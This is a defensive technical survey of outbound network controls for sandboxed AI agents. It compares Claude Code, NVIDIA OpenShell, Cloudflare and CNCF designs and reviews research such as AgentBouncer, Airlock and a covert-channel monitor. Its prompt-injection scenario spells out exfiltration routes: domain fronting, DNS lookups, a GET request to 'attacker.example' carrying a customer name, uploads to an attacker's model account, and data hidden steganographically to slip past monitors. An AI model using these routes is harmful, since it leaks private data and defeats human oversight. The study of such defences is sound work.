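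Methods and paths also reveal little about requests to services that use GraphQL, a query language in which a single address handles every operation and the request specifies whether to read or delete something. For these services, OpenShell parses the operation, so a policy can allow queries and block an operation called `deleteRepository`. For ordinary web interfaces, its rules cover the method, path and query parameters, but they don't check the text of a reply to a customer.

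A service can respond to the approved read with a redirect, which tells the client to fetch a different address. The safe course is for the adapter to return the redirect to the agent, whose library then makes a new request that the adapter checks from the beginning. An adapter that follows redirects itself has to repeat the destination check and remove the key, or an approved service could cause it to send the key to an unapproved address. Redirects can also require the operator to add hosts to the allowlist. If the ticketing service keeps attachments on a large shared storage host, the agent can't open them until the operator approves that host, where an attacker may also have an account.

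The adapter also decrypts the response, which contains the ticket and its hidden paragraph, and passes both to the agent. The injection therefore enters through a permitted read, and the rules on requests only limit what happens afterwards.

Finally, the adapter records both requests. According to NVIDIA's *What is the best way to control which external APIs an AI* (2026), OpenShell logs the destination, port, program and reason when it refuses a connection. The CNCF example produces one record per request in OpenTelemetry format, an open standard for monitoring data, so that a team can link a user's message to the outside calls that followed it.

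The adapter should write this log where the agent can't reach it. Pirch and colleagues tampered with the agents' own log files on OpenClaw, IronClaw and NemoClaw. *The Importance of Out-of-Band Metadata for Safe Autonomous Agents* (Akidau, Rockwood and colleagues, 2026) makes the same point about any audit trail that depends on the agent to report its own actions, since a compromised agent can leave out or invent entries.

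### How the adapter adds the key

The read needs a key, and the adapter adds it only after the request has passed every rule. In Cloudflare's version, which is the simplest, a few lines of JavaScript copy the request, add a header with the secret and send it on. The secret can differ between sandboxes. OpenShell and Claude Code can also use placeholders. The sandbox holds a meaningless string where a tool expects its key, and the adapter replaces the string with the real key on the way out. This suits tools that won't start without a key, and a script that prints the placeholder or sends it to a stranger doesn't reveal the real key.

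Placeholders only work if the adapter decrypts the traffic. In Claude Code, decryption is an experimental setting that operators have to turn on. Anthropic explains that if they don't, the placeholder reaches the service unchanged and the login fails, but the real key stays hidden.

The adapter also has to restrict each key to the service it belongs to. In Claude Code, an operator can list the hosts that may receive a key. Without that list, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real key in requests to any allowed host. A hijacked support agent could then put the ticketing placeholder in a request to the model service, and the proxy would send the real ticketing key there. NVIDIA prevents this by tying each placeholder to the hosts, ports and paths in the provider's profile.

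Restricting the host isn't always enough. OpenShell can also replace placeholders in a request's body, because some services expect the key there. NVIDIA leaves this off by default and recommends it only for services that need it. If the support team turned it on for the ticketing service, a hijacked agent could write the placeholder into a reply to the attacker. According to NVIDIA's description, the adapter would then replace the placeholder with the real key and post the reply.

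Some services don't accept a key in a header. Amazon's cloud requires a signature computed over the contents of the request, so Claude Code's proxy signs the request again with the real key. It can't do this for streaming uploads or for web addresses that already contain a signature, and it rejects those requests.

A hijacked support agent never holds the ticketing key, but it can still send the adapter unlimited requests for any operation the policy permits.

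### Address, server name or full request

The two requests show how much depends on the level at which the adapter inspects traffic. Only one level distinguishes them.

| Filtering by | What the adapter sees of the read | What it sees of the webhook request | What it can't stop |
|---|---|---|---|
| Numeric address | 203.0.113.20, port 443 | The same | Traffic to other sites at that address |
| Server name | api.tickets.example | The same | A false name, or misuse of the approved site |
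| Full request | GET /v1/tickets/4012 | POST /v1/webhooks | Data hidden in a permitted request |

Filtering by numeric address works well for the firewall around the sandbox, which only has to allow one fixed destination, the adapter. It works badly for outside services, because their addresses change and large hosting companies put thousands of unrelated sites behind the same addresses.

When a TLS connection opens, the client normally sends the server's name unencrypted in the Server Name Indication (SNI) field. An adapter can compare that name, or the name in a tunnel request, with its allowlist without decrypting anything. But the client supplies both names, and either can be false. In domain fronting, a program names an approved site when it opens a connection, then uses the encrypted connection to request another site on the same content delivery network. Anthropic warns that code in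 Claude Code's sandbox may be able to do this, because the built-in proxy checks only the requested hostname by default.

Apache Magpie's *Secure agent setup* includes an example of encrypted name lookups. Magpie is an Apache Software Foundation framework whose agents handle security reports before publication, and it runs Claude Code in the sandbox. When a program connects to Cloudflare's lookup service, the visible name is `cloudflare-dns.com`, but the encrypted query can be about any domain. If the lookup service is on the allowlist, the proxy can't block lookups that carry data.

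Data can still leak through an allowed domain when the server name is accurate. Magpie's allowlist includes `github.com` and all subdomains of `googleapis.com`, where anyone with an account can store data. Docker, whose agent sandboxes also filter by domain without reading the content, warns of the same risk with `github.com`.

An adapter that decrypts a request can detect domain fronting by comparing the site named inside the encrypted request with the one named outside it. OpenShell requires the two to match whenever it decrypts web traffic. However, an adapter can decrypt a request without restricting its content. Claude Code's experimental setting decrypts traffic to substitute keys but adds no content filter. OpenShell decrypts traffic to every listed web service but allows any method and path if the operator doesn't specify a protocol for that service. Operators comparing products should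 therefore check what each adapter does with decrypted requests.

Rules that permit only reading can also create false confidence, because an agent can put data in the address it requests. Cloudflare's first example is a handler that allows GET requests to any host and blocks all other requests. This would stop the webhook, but a GET request for `attacker.example/?name=jane-smith` would still deliver the name, just as a POST request would. The example also needs a list of permitted hosts, which Cloudflare provides as a separate setting.

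### A policy for the support agent

In the format of NVIDIA's schema, the network part of the support agent's policy could look like this:

```yaml
version: 1
network_policies:
  ticketing:
    endpoints:
      - host: api.tickets.example
        port: 443
        protocol: rest
        enforcement: enforce
        rules:
          - allow: { method: GET,  path: "/v1/tickets/*" }
          - allow: { method: GET,  path: "/v1/customers/*" }
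          - allow: { method: POST, path: "/v1/tickets/*/replies" }
    binaries:
      - path: /usr/local/bin/support-agent
  model:
    endpoints:
      - host: api.model.example
        port: 443
        protocol: rest
        enforcement: enforce
        rules:
          - allow: { method: POST, path: "/v1/chat/completions" }
    binaries:
      - path: /usr/local/bin/support-agent
```

The agent may read or reply to a ticket, read a customer's record, and call the model. OpenShell blocks everything else, including the webhook. The customer rule allows requests for one record at a time but not for the full list, so a hijacked agent would have to make two hundred requests to collect two hundred addresses, which would stand out in the log.

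NVIDIA also offers preset access levels, but they don't suit this agent. The read-only level would block its replies. The read-write level permits POST requests to any path, so it would allow the webhook unless an operator added a separate rule to deny it. Listing the three permitted operations takes longer but is safer, because any new feature of the ticketing service stays blocked until someone adds it to the list.

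The policy reduces the number of request forms but doesn't limit what a reply contains. The schema has no field for the text of an ordinary web request or for a quota, so to bound N × log2(K), the operator has to limit both the free text and the number of requests by other means. Akidau and colleagues, who work for the data company Redpanda, use a counter in the gateway to enforce limits such as ten trades an hour.

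OpenShell applies changes to these network rules without restarting the sandbox. According to NVIDIA, when an agent requests an unlisted destination, OpenShell blocks the request and shows it to an operator. If the operator approves it, the destination is added to the running sandbox and stays allowed until the sandbox is destroyed. This is convenient for exploratory work, but it conflicts with Silverlock's advice that an approved change should apply only to future tasks. If the task that made the request has been hijacked, the approval gives that same task access to the destination.

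### Four designs on the same points

| Design | Where the adapter runs | What it inspects | Who holds the credentials | Default |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code deployment guide | On the host, outside the container or virtual machine | Hostname, or the full request if the operator installs a proxy that decrypts | The proxy | No network until the operator connects the proxy |
| NVIDIA OpenShell | In a trusted supervisor, which the agent reaches through a private channel | Program, host and port, plus method and path if the operator specifies them | OpenShell's credential store | Unlisted destinations refused, but method and path violations only logged |
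| Cloudflare outbound Workers | On the same machine, outside the sandbox | Whatever the operator's code examines | The Worker's settings or key store | Open internet until the operator restricts it |
| CNCF NGINX example | In a separate container in the same cluster | Domain | No injection described | Two permitted domains |

Deployed systems differ most in their defaults. Cloudflare sandboxes can reach the public internet unless the operator sets `enableInternet` to false or supplies a list of allowed hosts. Even with internet access off, they can look up names through Cloudflare's DNS servers. An operator should test whether those servers resolve unlisted names, because that would open the lookup route that simedw blocks.

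Claude Code is less restricted by default than the deployment guide recommends, and its sandbox for shell commands is off. According to Anthropic, if an operator turns the sandbox on but a required component is missing, Claude Code runs commands without it unless another setting tells it to stop. If the sandbox blocks a command, Claude can also ask to rerun it outside the sandbox. A person normally has to approve the retry, but one permission mode skips that step. For organizations that require sandboxing, Anthropic suggests settings that turn off these retries and make Claude Code exit when the sandbox is unavailable.

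OpenShell's adapter, the supervisor, seems to have moved out of the agent's container. An older NVIDIA overview describes a supervisor that runs inside each sandbox and starts the agent as a restricted process. The security page describes a container that has no network and reaches the supervisor through a private socket. The newer arrangement is closer to Anderson's requirement of protection against tampering, because an agent that breaks out of its restricted process no longer shares a container with the adapter.

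Cloudflare's rules are programs, which can do more than OpenShell's lists. A program can enforce permissions that the outside service lacks, or open the npm package registry while a sandbox installs its software and close it before the agent begins work. Cloudflare's *Handle outbound traffic* shows how to add and remove access this way. But a program is harder to review than a short list, which a reviewer can check by reading. A program may behave differently from how it looks, and a mistake in it may permit more than its author intended.

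Code in the adapter can also help with permissions on individual records, which an ordinary adapter can't check. Cloudflare's example uses the sandbox's identity to select a storage folder, so each sandbox can read only its own files. In a demonstration by Akidau and colleagues, agents manage investments for several clients, and the gateway inserts the client's identity into each request for account data. The model never supplies a client number, so it can't request another client's data. The support team could start one sandbox per ticket and have the adapter add the customer number. The agent would then see only that customer's record, and an order to collect two hundred addresses would fail at the collection step, before any attempt to send them out.

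The CNCF example is a proof of concept. Its author calls it a passion project and ran it on one machine, with firewall rules that drop all traffic that bypasses NGINX. It shows that a team can build the basic pattern from standard open-source parts, but it doesn't cover method rules or keys.

### The model service as an exit

The support agent sends more private data to the model service than anywhere else. Each call includes the ticket, the customer's record and whatever the agent's scripts have printed, because the model needs them to choose the next step. The company accepted this when it chose the provider, but it did not agree to send data to another customer's account there. The hidden paragraph can contain the attacker's own key for the model service and an instruction to upload a file with it. Because the service's hostname is on the allowlist, the upload goes through and the file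 arrives in the attacker's account. Anthropic changed its own proxy after files left one of its products by a similar route.

The adapter can narrow this exit by allowing only certain operations. On NVIDIA's own model service, NemoClaw can only list the available models and request a completion, and NVIDIA permits these requests only from named programs. An upload to a file store on the same host would fail.

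The adapter can also control whose account receives the request. NVIDIA's *About Inference Routing* describes a special local address for model calls, where OpenShell replaces the agent's credentials with the operator's. Even if the agent uses an attacker's key, the data goes to the operator's account. A placeholder alone doesn't provide this protection. If the agent writes the attacker's key instead of the placeholder, the adapter has nothing to replace, and the request could go out with that key unless the adapter rejects keys it did not supply. NVIDIA's current documentation describes placeholders for the major model providers, so operators should test this case.

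Anthropic's guide includes a simpler technique for model calls. The `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` setting makes Claude Code send them unencrypted to the proxy, which encrypts them for the provider. This lets the proxy read the request and add the key without a special certificate. The setting covers only model calls, so requests to the ticketing service still need decryption or a tool that runs outside the sandbox.

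Redpanda sends every model call through what it calls an AI gateway. Agents identify themselves with their own credentials, and the gateway limits each agent's spending and request rate, screens prompts and responses, and chooses the model. Akidau and colleagues argue that an agent cannot bypass the gateway because it never holds a model provider's key. That follows only if the agent has no other network route, since an attacker can supply their own key. In their demonstration, the agents ran on Google's cloud, outside Redpanda's platform, so someone would have to block the other routes there.

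An agent doesn't need outbound access to a model provider if the model runs locally. The CNCF example uses Ollama, a program that runs models on the operator's own hardware, in the same cluster as the agent. No prompt needs to leave the cluster, but the operator has to provide the hardware and accept the local model's quality.

### Where the agent loop runs

So far the harness that calls the model and the scripts the model writes, which together make up the whole agent, have both been inside the sandbox. The harness needs a route from the sandbox to the model service, and the scripts can use that route too.

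The operator can instead run the harness outside the sandbox and only the scripts inside it. The scripts then don't need a route to the model service or access to its key. The support agent's log searches don't need the network, so their sandbox could omit even the socket to the adapter. Their output would still reach the model, which might include it in a reply, but a script could no longer send anything itself or exploit a bug in the adapter.

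The disadvantage is that everything the harness does now happens outside the sandbox. Claude Code works this way by default, and its tools for reading files and fetching web pages follow separate permission rules. Anthropic states that the sandbox's list of allowed domains doesn't limit the web-fetching tool. A hijacked model could therefore call that tool with an address that contains customer data, even though the operator approved only two domains and might believe that the agent can reach nothing else. Whether the tool makes the request depends on its permission rules, which are checked in the agent's own program.

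Moving the harness out of the sandbox is therefore safe only if the harness has its own boundary. The support agent's scripts could run in an inner sandbox with no network access, and its harness could run in an outer sandbox that connects only to the adapter. For Claude Code, following Anthropic's advice to enclose the entire process provides the outer sandbox.

### What the designs cost

The most obvious drawback is lost access. The support agent can't open a customer's link to a screenshot on an unlisted site. Traffic to approved services can also fail if it doesn't use ordinary web protocols. Anthropic reports that in Claude Code's sandbox, most database programs and plain `ssh` (a tool for logging in to other machines) can't connect even to an allowed host, because they ignore the proxy settings. HTTP/3, the newest version of the web protocol, doesn't work either. Docker's sandboxes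 block everything that doesn't go through their web proxy. OpenShell can relay database connections but applies no rules to their content.

Decryption causes other failures. Every program has to trust the adapter's CA, and different programming languages look for trusted certificates in different places, so OpenShell sets six variables. Some services require the client to prove its identity with its own certificate, which the adapter can't do on the client's behalf. NVIDIA's answer is to turn off decryption for those services, which also turns off key substitution and the method rules. On macOS, some common tools for GitHub and Google's cloud may reject certificates inside Claude Code's sandbox. Anthropic suggests running those tools outside the sandbox or, for operators who use their own decrypting proxy, turning on a weaker form of isolation.

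Apache Magpie shows how such exceptions accumulate. It runs GitHub's command-line tool outside the sandbox, where no network filter applies, and relies on a person to confirm each action that changes something. It also uses the weaker isolation on macOS, which opens another route through a system service. These are considerable concessions to convenience for a team that handles unpublished vulnerabilities. The documentation lists these gaps and recommends a separate firewall on machines where they matter.

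There is little evidence on how much an adapter slows an agent down. Cloudflare claims that the added delay is "extremely minimal" because the proxy runs on the same machine as the sandbox, but it gives no measurement. A local proxy probably makes little difference to an agent that waits seconds for each answer from a model. Large requests could be a greater problem, because an adapter that examines the body has to hold it in memory. OpenShell buffers at most 256 KiB when it replaces keys in a request body, and 64 KiB by default when it inspects GraphQL.

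All four designs need ongoing maintenance. The CNCF author acknowledges that the proxy is one more component to secure and monitor, and Anthropic mentions the extra work of managing certificates. NVIDIA advises operators to start with a minimal allowlist and use the log of refused requests to find what is missing. A setting's effect can also change between releases. Before version 2.1.285 of Claude Code, a project's files could re-enable unsandboxed retries that a user had turned off in personal settings.

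### How common such filtering is

Few agents had filtering of this kind in 2026, judging by the small sample that Pirch and colleagues examined. They divided open-source assistants into four groups and chose the most popular project from each. Apart from NemoClaw, only IronClaw had any network filtering, and its allowlist covers tools that run in its own sandbox but not tools it reaches through MCP.

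The unfiltered design was also by far the most popular. In May 2026, OpenClaw had about 366,000 GitHub stars (user bookmarks), and NemoClaw had about 20,000. Stars show interest rather than installations, and NemoClaw was only two months old. Four projects are too few to estimate a rate for agents in general. The researchers left out coding agents and hosted services because their makers control the environment more tightly.

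Many installations of products that include an adapter may not use it fully, because Claude Code, Cloudflare and OpenShell all leave some of the protection off by default. Pirch and colleagues argue that a system should be reasonably secure without expert configuration.

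## Experiments that measure outbound control

Few researchers have measured how well an outbound adapter works. In *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, Rashidi (2026) sorted 39 papers on the security of agents' working environments into 17 categories. As of July 2026, only one of the 39 was in the network egress control category, compared with six in access control and five in isolation. Rashidi warns that the search may have missed papers, and it missed at least one, Metere's May 2026 paper on a covert-channel monitor. At least two more studies of outbound traffic appeared later that year.

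That still leaves only about half a dozen studies. Between them, they test whether a connection can bypass the control, how well the control evaluates requests, whether it survives an attack on the machine it runs on, and how much data leaves inside permitted messages.

### Can a connection get past the control?

*Connection Escrow* (Gopalakrishna, 2026) studies an agent running in a Kubernetes pod, a group of containers that share a network address. In its threat model, the attacker controls all the code in the pod and can start new processes, rename programs and open any kind of connection, but can't break out of the pod or take over the machine it runs on.

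When a program in the pod requests a connection from the Linux kernel, a small program inside the kernel replaces the requested address with that of an interceptor on the same machine. The kernel hasn't sent anything yet, so the real destination receives no sign of the attempt. The interceptor identifies the program and the pod, reads the first bytes of the request and consults a verifier, which runs in a separate container with its own signing key. Each approval is for one connection to one destination and can be used only once. If no valid approval arrives before a deadline (one second in the tests), the interceptor resets the connection. OpenShell's approvals are much looser, because they open a destination for as long as the sandbox exists.

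This system passed all 36 checks that Gopalakrishna wrote for it. In some, a child process or a renamed copy of the Python interpreter tried to connect. In others, the interceptor received a forged, expired or reused approval, or the verifier was down. These are pass-or-fail tests of stated rules, so the result does not estimate what share of attacks the system would stop. Gopalakrishna did not run the system on a set of agent tasks either, so the results do not show how much legitimate work it would refuse.

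The paper also compares Connection Escrow with a proxy that the agent's programs find through an environment variable. The proxy blocked an ordinary web request, but a raw socket bypassed it and delivered the data. Connection Escrow stopped both. However, simedw had already bypassed this weak proxy arrangement, and a firewall that drops all traffic except to the proxy would also have stopped the raw socket. The comparison is good evidence for forcing traffic through a checkpoint, but it doesn't show that Connection Escrow does this better than a firewall.

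The system doesn't stop data from leaving in name lookups, because programs can query the cluster's own name server before they ask for a connection. The prototype also doesn't handle IPv6, the newer addressing system, so an operator would have to block it separately.

The delay is small compared with the seconds an agent can spend waiting for a model's answer. With everything on one machine, the system held each approved connection for a median of 4.3 milliseconds, of which the policy decision took 0.024. When six pods opened 600 connections on a small cluster, the median rose to 18 milliseconds. Requiring a person to approve a connection adds a longer delay, and the connection can fail if the deadline passes first.

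*AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) shows why a control should decide whether to allow a connection before it opens. One system tested in the paper, AgentSentinel, watches what programs do and kills any process that does something unsafe. In 24 of 340 attacks, the full damage occurred even though AgentSentinel killed the process. In another 37, part of the damage occurred. For example, a request carrying stolen data reached the attacker with its end cut off.

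### Can a model judge each request?

Most deployed adapters use fixed rules to filter outbound traffic. Joos and Pradel's AgentBouncer uses fixed rules for routine actions and a language model for the rest.

Joos and Pradel assume that the user, the operating system and the model provider can be trusted. The attacker can plant text in the agent's prompt, supply a malicious tool, or put harmful code in the agent's environment or in the repository it works on. AgentBouncer intercepts the system calls that programs use to open files, start processes and connect to the network. It permits network connections only within the machine and to its own proxy. The proxy decrypts each web request and extracts the method, the full address and the body.

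If neither a fixed rule nor an earlier decision covers a request, AgentBouncer sends it to a model called the arbiter. The arbiter uses the user's task, the agent's current tool call and the agent's stated reason for that call to assess whether the request is safe and whether the task needs it. It refuses any unsafe request, however useful, and requires more confidence that a request is safe when the task seems to need it less.

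The experiment used a coding agent on problems from SWE-bench Verified, a collection of real software issues with hidden tests that check each fix. Joos and Pradel chose 85 harmful goals, such as sending a file to an outside server or overwriting cloud credentials, and tried each of them in four ways:

- a command in the task description, presented as a necessary set-up step
- a tool that did its advertised job and secretly ran the attack as well
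- a planted script, which the task description called a mandatory check
- code in the repository that ran the attack when the agent ran the tests

The attacks totalled 340. The table compares AgentBouncer with an unsupervised agent and five other defences. Joos and Pradel used LlamaGuard, a model that classifies text as safe or unsafe, in two ways.

| Defence | What it checks | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks solved with no attack | Harmless tool calls that failed because of it |
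|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | Nothing | 99.41% | 71.47% | Not applicable |
| AgentSpec | Tool calls, against fixed rules | 28.82% | 63.53% | 25.87% |
| LlamaGuard-Prompt | The initial prompt | 84.12% | 75.29% | Not applicable |
| LlamaGuard-Tool | Each tool call | 11.47% | 1.18% | 71.57% |
| Drift | Tool calls, against a plan | 83.53% | 67.06% | 1.04% |
| AgentSentinel | Events, after they happen | 33.82% | 76.47% | 2.48% |
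| AgentBouncer | System calls and web requests, before they happen | 10.59% | 72.94% | 0.25% |

LlamaGuard-Tool stopped almost as many attacks as AgentBouncer, but only by refusing most tool calls, so the agent solved almost none of its tasks. Drift and LlamaGuard-Prompt missed most attacks because the harmful action never appeared in the text they checked. AgentBouncer blocked part of the activity in 3.42% of harmless tool calls, but most of those calls still finished.

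Many of the 340 attacks involved only local files, so the overall success rate of 10.59% is less relevant to outbound control than the results for the 100 attacks that used the network. AgentBouncer allowed the connection to the attacker in two of those 100. AgentSentinel, which has no access to the address or body of a web request, classified the connection as safe in 32. The two systems differ in other ways, but this comparison is the best available evidence that reading the full request helps.

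One attack read a system configuration file and posted it to a host whose name resembled a telemetry service's. The arbiter usually allowed the read, which is harmless by itself, but always refused the upload. Uploading system files to an unknown server is fairly easy to recognise as an attack. The support agent's reply to a customer would be harder to judge, because the agent is supposed to send replies and the ticketing service is a legitimate destination.

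A model's decisions also vary. An allowlist refuses a forbidden address every time, but a model that refuses a request today may accept a slightly reworded one tomorrow. If each attempt had an independent 2% chance of getting through, an attacker with a hundred attempts would have about an 87% chance of succeeding at least once (1 − 0.98^100). The 2% comes from a hundred different attacks, not repeats of one, so the calculation only illustrates the danger of relying on a low average. Injected text can also influence the arbiter through the task description. The two kinds of attack that altered the description succeeded 14.12% of the time, compared with 7.06% for the other two. Joos and Pradel note that most of these successes were not clearly harmful actions.

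When Joos and Pradel removed the arbiter and refused everything outside the 60 fixed rules, no attack succeeded, but the agent solved only 8.24% of its tasks. The main cause was refused file writes, so the result is only weak evidence of how a strict network allowlist would affect task completion. The table also doesn't include an ordinary allowlist proxy, so the experiment can't show whether a model controls outbound requests better than a short list of addresses would.

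The arbiter added 47 seconds to a task that took about a minute without it, and raised the model cost by 38%, or USD 0.0036. An average task involved 28,167 decisions, and the fixed rules and stored decisions handled all but about eight of them. Joos and Pradel estimate that sending every decision to the model would take 25.5 hours and cost USD 13 per task.

The shortcuts also create a weakness. After the arbiter allows one read-only web request, it can approve every address that begins the same way, and the model does not check later requests to those addresses. Since the address of a GET request can carry data, the agent could send data this way to any approved site whose incoming requests the attacker can see. Overly broad stored approvals accounted for two of the 36 successful attacks in the experiment. The example Joos and Pradel give of such an attack involved a local file.

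Gopalakrishna's Connection Escrow also had a problem with checking only once. An optional part of the system reads messages inside the agent's encryption library, just before encryption, so it can inspect content without impersonating the destination. The first version checked only the first message on a connection. In a test, the agent sent a harmless request and then, on the same connection, a number that looked like a payment card's. The second request went through. A revised version checks every message and stopped the second request.

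This arrangement avoids the certificate problems that decryption causes, but it offers weaker protection than the hold on connections. A hostile program can encrypt messages with its own code, so the system can't read them. The system blocks such connections, but Gopalakrishna concedes that the program could also show the system a harmless decoy and send the real data another way. The tests used a placeholder classifier, so they show that the system can capture and hold messages, but not that it can recognise theft in real traffic.

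### Can the adapter survive an attack on its own machine?

AgentBouncer and Connection Escrow both trust the operating system beneath them, but *Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) does not. In its threat model, the agent may be malicious from the start and may take over its entire virtual machine, including the kernel. The host's operating system may also be malicious and may help the agent.

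Airlock uses two virtual machines, which the processor isolates from each other and from the host. One contains the agent and its tools, and the other contains OpenShell's supervisor, the policies, the real credentials and the log. The agent's machine has no network card or disk. Its only outside connections are a channel for network requests and a file system, and the second machine provides both. So an agent that takes over its machine's kernel can send any request, but each one must still pass the policy in the second machine.

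This design uses attestation to check that the second machine is running the right software. When a protected virtual machine starts, trusted firmware computes a hash of what it loads, such as the kernel and its start-up options. The firmware can later issue a statement containing that hash, signed with a key that traces back to the hardware. The statement also includes a fresh number supplied with the request, so nobody can pass off an old statement as new. A person or program elsewhere checks the signature and compares the hash with the expected value. Pinning specifies which version of the adapter should run, and attestation gives evidence of whether that version started. Attestation doesn't show that the software is free of bugs or that nobody has compromised it since it started.

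In Airlock, each of the two virtual machines has a policy that identifies the other by its hash. The firmware compares both policies with its own measurements and opens a shared area of memory only if they match. It also stops the agent's machine from sharing memory with the host. The connection policy can't change after that, even if the agent controls its own kernel.

Airlock also protects the log against a later break-in. The second machine sends its records to an outside ledger that accepts new entries but never changes or deletes old ones. A new HTTPS connection waits until the ledger has stored its record. If an attacker takes over the second machine, the earlier records survive, although a few seconds of file accesses, name lookups and unencrypted requests may be missing. This addresses a known weakness, since Pirch and colleagues tampered with the logs of three assistants.

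Abdollahi and colleagues argue for these guarantees from the design, and their argument depends on a fairly large amount of trusted software, including the firmware, the supervisor and the second machine's whole Linux kernel. That is far too much to analyze completely, as Anderson requires. They exclude physical attacks and the misuse of services that the policy allows, so Airlock would still forward a reply containing the customer list.

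The slowdown is hard to judge because no commercial processor with the necessary Arm features was available. Abdollahi and colleagues used an emulator to test whether the system worked, and measured its speed on a small development board that imitates the missing features in software. File performance and the delay for small messages worsened by less than 15%. Network throughput fell by 51 to 70% compared with a supervisor in the same virtual machine as the agent. This drop in throughput would matter for an agent that moves large files but probably not for one that reads tickets.

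### What if the adapter's operator is the attacker?

Whoever controls an adapter that decrypts traffic can read everything that passes through it. This matters more when a company relies on somebody else's adapter than when it runs its own. Many agents reach model providers through a router, a service that offers several providers behind one address and handles the accounts and billing. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (Xie, Wu and colleagues, 2026) examines what a malicious router operator could do and how to prevent it.

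A router sees the user's prompts and the model's replies, including the tool calls that the agent will carry out. Its operator could change a shell command in a reply, and the agent would run the altered version. The operator could also replace the name of a software package with the similar name of a malicious one. The operator could make either change only after a particular keyword or number of requests, so that an auditor who sends a few test requests sees nothing wrong. Or the operator could simply search the traffic for passwords and keys.

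Xie and colleagues built a router called AEGIS, in which only the code that carries requests and replies can read them. That code runs in an enclave, an area of the processor that the rest of the computer can't read or change. Logins, billing and the choice of account are handled outside the enclave. Before the agent's computer sends any content, a small local program uses attestation to check the hash of the enclave's software. The hash covers the list of permitted destinations, so the operator can't quietly add one, as they could if it covered only the rest of the code.

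All four attacks succeeded against an ordinary router, but AEGIS blocked them all. It completed every request in tests with real providers and added about six milliseconds to each. The part that handles readable traffic is 851 lines long, so it comes much closer to meeting Anderson's size condition than most adapters do. To test whether people could audit it, Xie and colleagues planted ten violations of its security rules and asked two commercial coding agents to find them. One found eight and the other found all ten. The trial was tiny and the researchers chose the faults themselves, but it suggests that code of this size is practical to review.

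The operator still learns the length and timing of each message, which account and provider handled it, and how many tokens it used. The design also assumes that the provider is honest, and it does not address attacks that extract data from the enclave through physical effects.

AEGIS protects users from the router's operator but not from a hijacked agent. It forwards every request unread and unchanged, so a stolen customer list inside a prompt would reach the provider. To block the list, code inside the enclave would have to inspect requests, and each added rule would make the trusted part larger and harder to audit.

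### How much data leaves inside permitted messages?

Rashidi files only one paper under network egress control, and it deals with the content of messages instead of network connections. *Firewalls to Secure Dynamic LLM Agentic Networks* (Abdelnabi, Gomaa and colleagues, 2025) considers a personal assistant that books travel, looks for housing or buys insurance by talking to other companies' agents. One of these agents may try to extract private information over several turns or talk the assistant into a bad deal. The assistant has to keep talking to it, so blocking the destination isn't an option.

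The first of the two firewalls handles incoming messages. A language model converts each message into a fixed set of fields, such as room type and price per night, with no field for flattery, false urgency or hidden orders. An ordinary program then checks every field and discards anything the format doesn't permit. This check doesn't depend on the model behaving correctly, because a manipulated field still has to pass it. Hotel names and other free text could contain instructions, so the firewall replaces them with labels such as "hotel_1" and restores the originals when the assistant replies.

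The second firewall reduces the detail of private data before the assistant sees it. A home address becomes "departing from the Paris area", and an exact age becomes "adult". The other agent can't influence this step because the firewall never reads that agent's messages. The assistant can't leak the details that were removed, even if someone persuades it to try, because it never received them.

The tests used ConVerse, a benchmark with 12 invented users and 864 attacks across travel, property and insurance. With GPT-5 as the assistant, the firewalls cut the success rate of privacy attacks from 84% to 10%, and of attempts to manipulate the assistant from 60% to 3%. Abdelnabi and colleagues report that the assistant completed its tasks as well as it did without the firewalls, and sometimes better.

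These results and the leakage bound both support limiting messages to fixed forms. The results are less encouraging for agents that need free text. Abdelnabi and colleagues acknowledge that the method can't work for a general tool such as a search assistant, because it has to read whatever it finds. A support desk falls in between. The firewall could reduce a billing complaint to a customer number, an invoice number and an amount, but it would lose most of a long description of a software fault. The firewall also doesn't restrict network access, so an adapter would still have to close the other routes.

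*An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* deals with data hidden in messages that look harmless. A secret scanner searches for recognisable text, such as the standard opening of a cloud key, so it finds nothing if the agent turns the key into bits and encodes them in the spaces between words. Metere assumes that the attacker controls what the agent tries to send and when, and knows how the defence works, but doesn't control the monitor or the system that runs it.

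An agent can hide data in text in many ways. It can insert characters that take up no space on the screen, or replace a Latin "o" with the identical-looking Cyrillic letter. It can also vary the order of fields in structured data, or choose between synonyms. Images and sound can hold more hidden data than text. An image, for example, can carry it in tiny changes to the colour of each pixel.

The monitor first removes invisible characters from each text message, replaces lookalike letters and puts fields into a standard order, none of which changes what a reader sees. It then blocks known credentials and estimates how much hidden data the message could hold. For example, n characters of base64, a common way to write data as text, can hold up to 6n bits. Each destination has an allowance for hidden data that refills over time. The monitor subtracts its estimates from this allowance and delays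 or blocks suspicious messages when it runs out. Later steps standardise wording and can have a separate model rewrite the whole message. The last steps control when messages leave and how often.

For pictures, the monitor rounds each colour channel to 64 levels, which destroys data in the two lowest bits. Sound is harder because an agent can turn data into audible tones, and no classifier can reliably distinguish them from real audio. The monitor therefore alters all images and sound, without trying to classify them, unless they carry a signature from a source the operator approved at startup.

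To measure what gets past the monitor, Metere hid data using fifteen encoding methods and compared it with what a receiver could recover after monitoring. Zero bits got through every channel that the monitor can destroy. One channel survived with limited capacity. An agent can still signal through the overall brightness of a series of images, because removing that signal completely would ruin the images.

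Unlike the N × log2(K) bound, the measurement of zero bits covers only the fifteen encodings that Metere tried, so other encodings might still carry information. The rewriting step also has to preserve the message's meaning. It can remove a signal in the wording, but a signal in the advice itself, such as whether to restart a program or reinstall it, should survive. Metere accepts that an agent can always convey one bit by sending a message or staying silent.

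Two design choices weaken the monitor further. Most failures block the message, but if the rewriting model is unavailable, the message goes out without being rewritten. If an attacker takes over an approved source of images or sound, the monitor lets that source's signed files through unchanged.

### Why the results don't produce a ranking

An operator can't choose among these designs by comparing their scores, because 36 passed checks, a 10.59% success rate against a coding agent and zero bits from fifteen encodings measure different things against different attackers. AgentBouncer's test against five other defences comes closest to a fair comparison, because all of them faced the same agent, tasks and attacks. But Joos and Pradel ran the test themselves and had to adapt some of the other defences to their agent.

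Researchers in this field mostly choose the attacks used to test their own systems. Gopalakrishna wrote the 36 checks and Metere the fifteen encoders, while Gomaa is first author of the ConVerse benchmark and joint first author of the firewall paper that uses it. The results may still be right, but people tend to test for the problems they had in mind when they designed the system. Xie and colleagues took their four kinds of attack from an earlier study of malicious routers, which is somewhat more independent. Joos and Pradel started from the public RedCode-Exec collection but dropped 8 of its 25 categories and rewrote others, so their figures are not directly comparable with those of other studies that use it.

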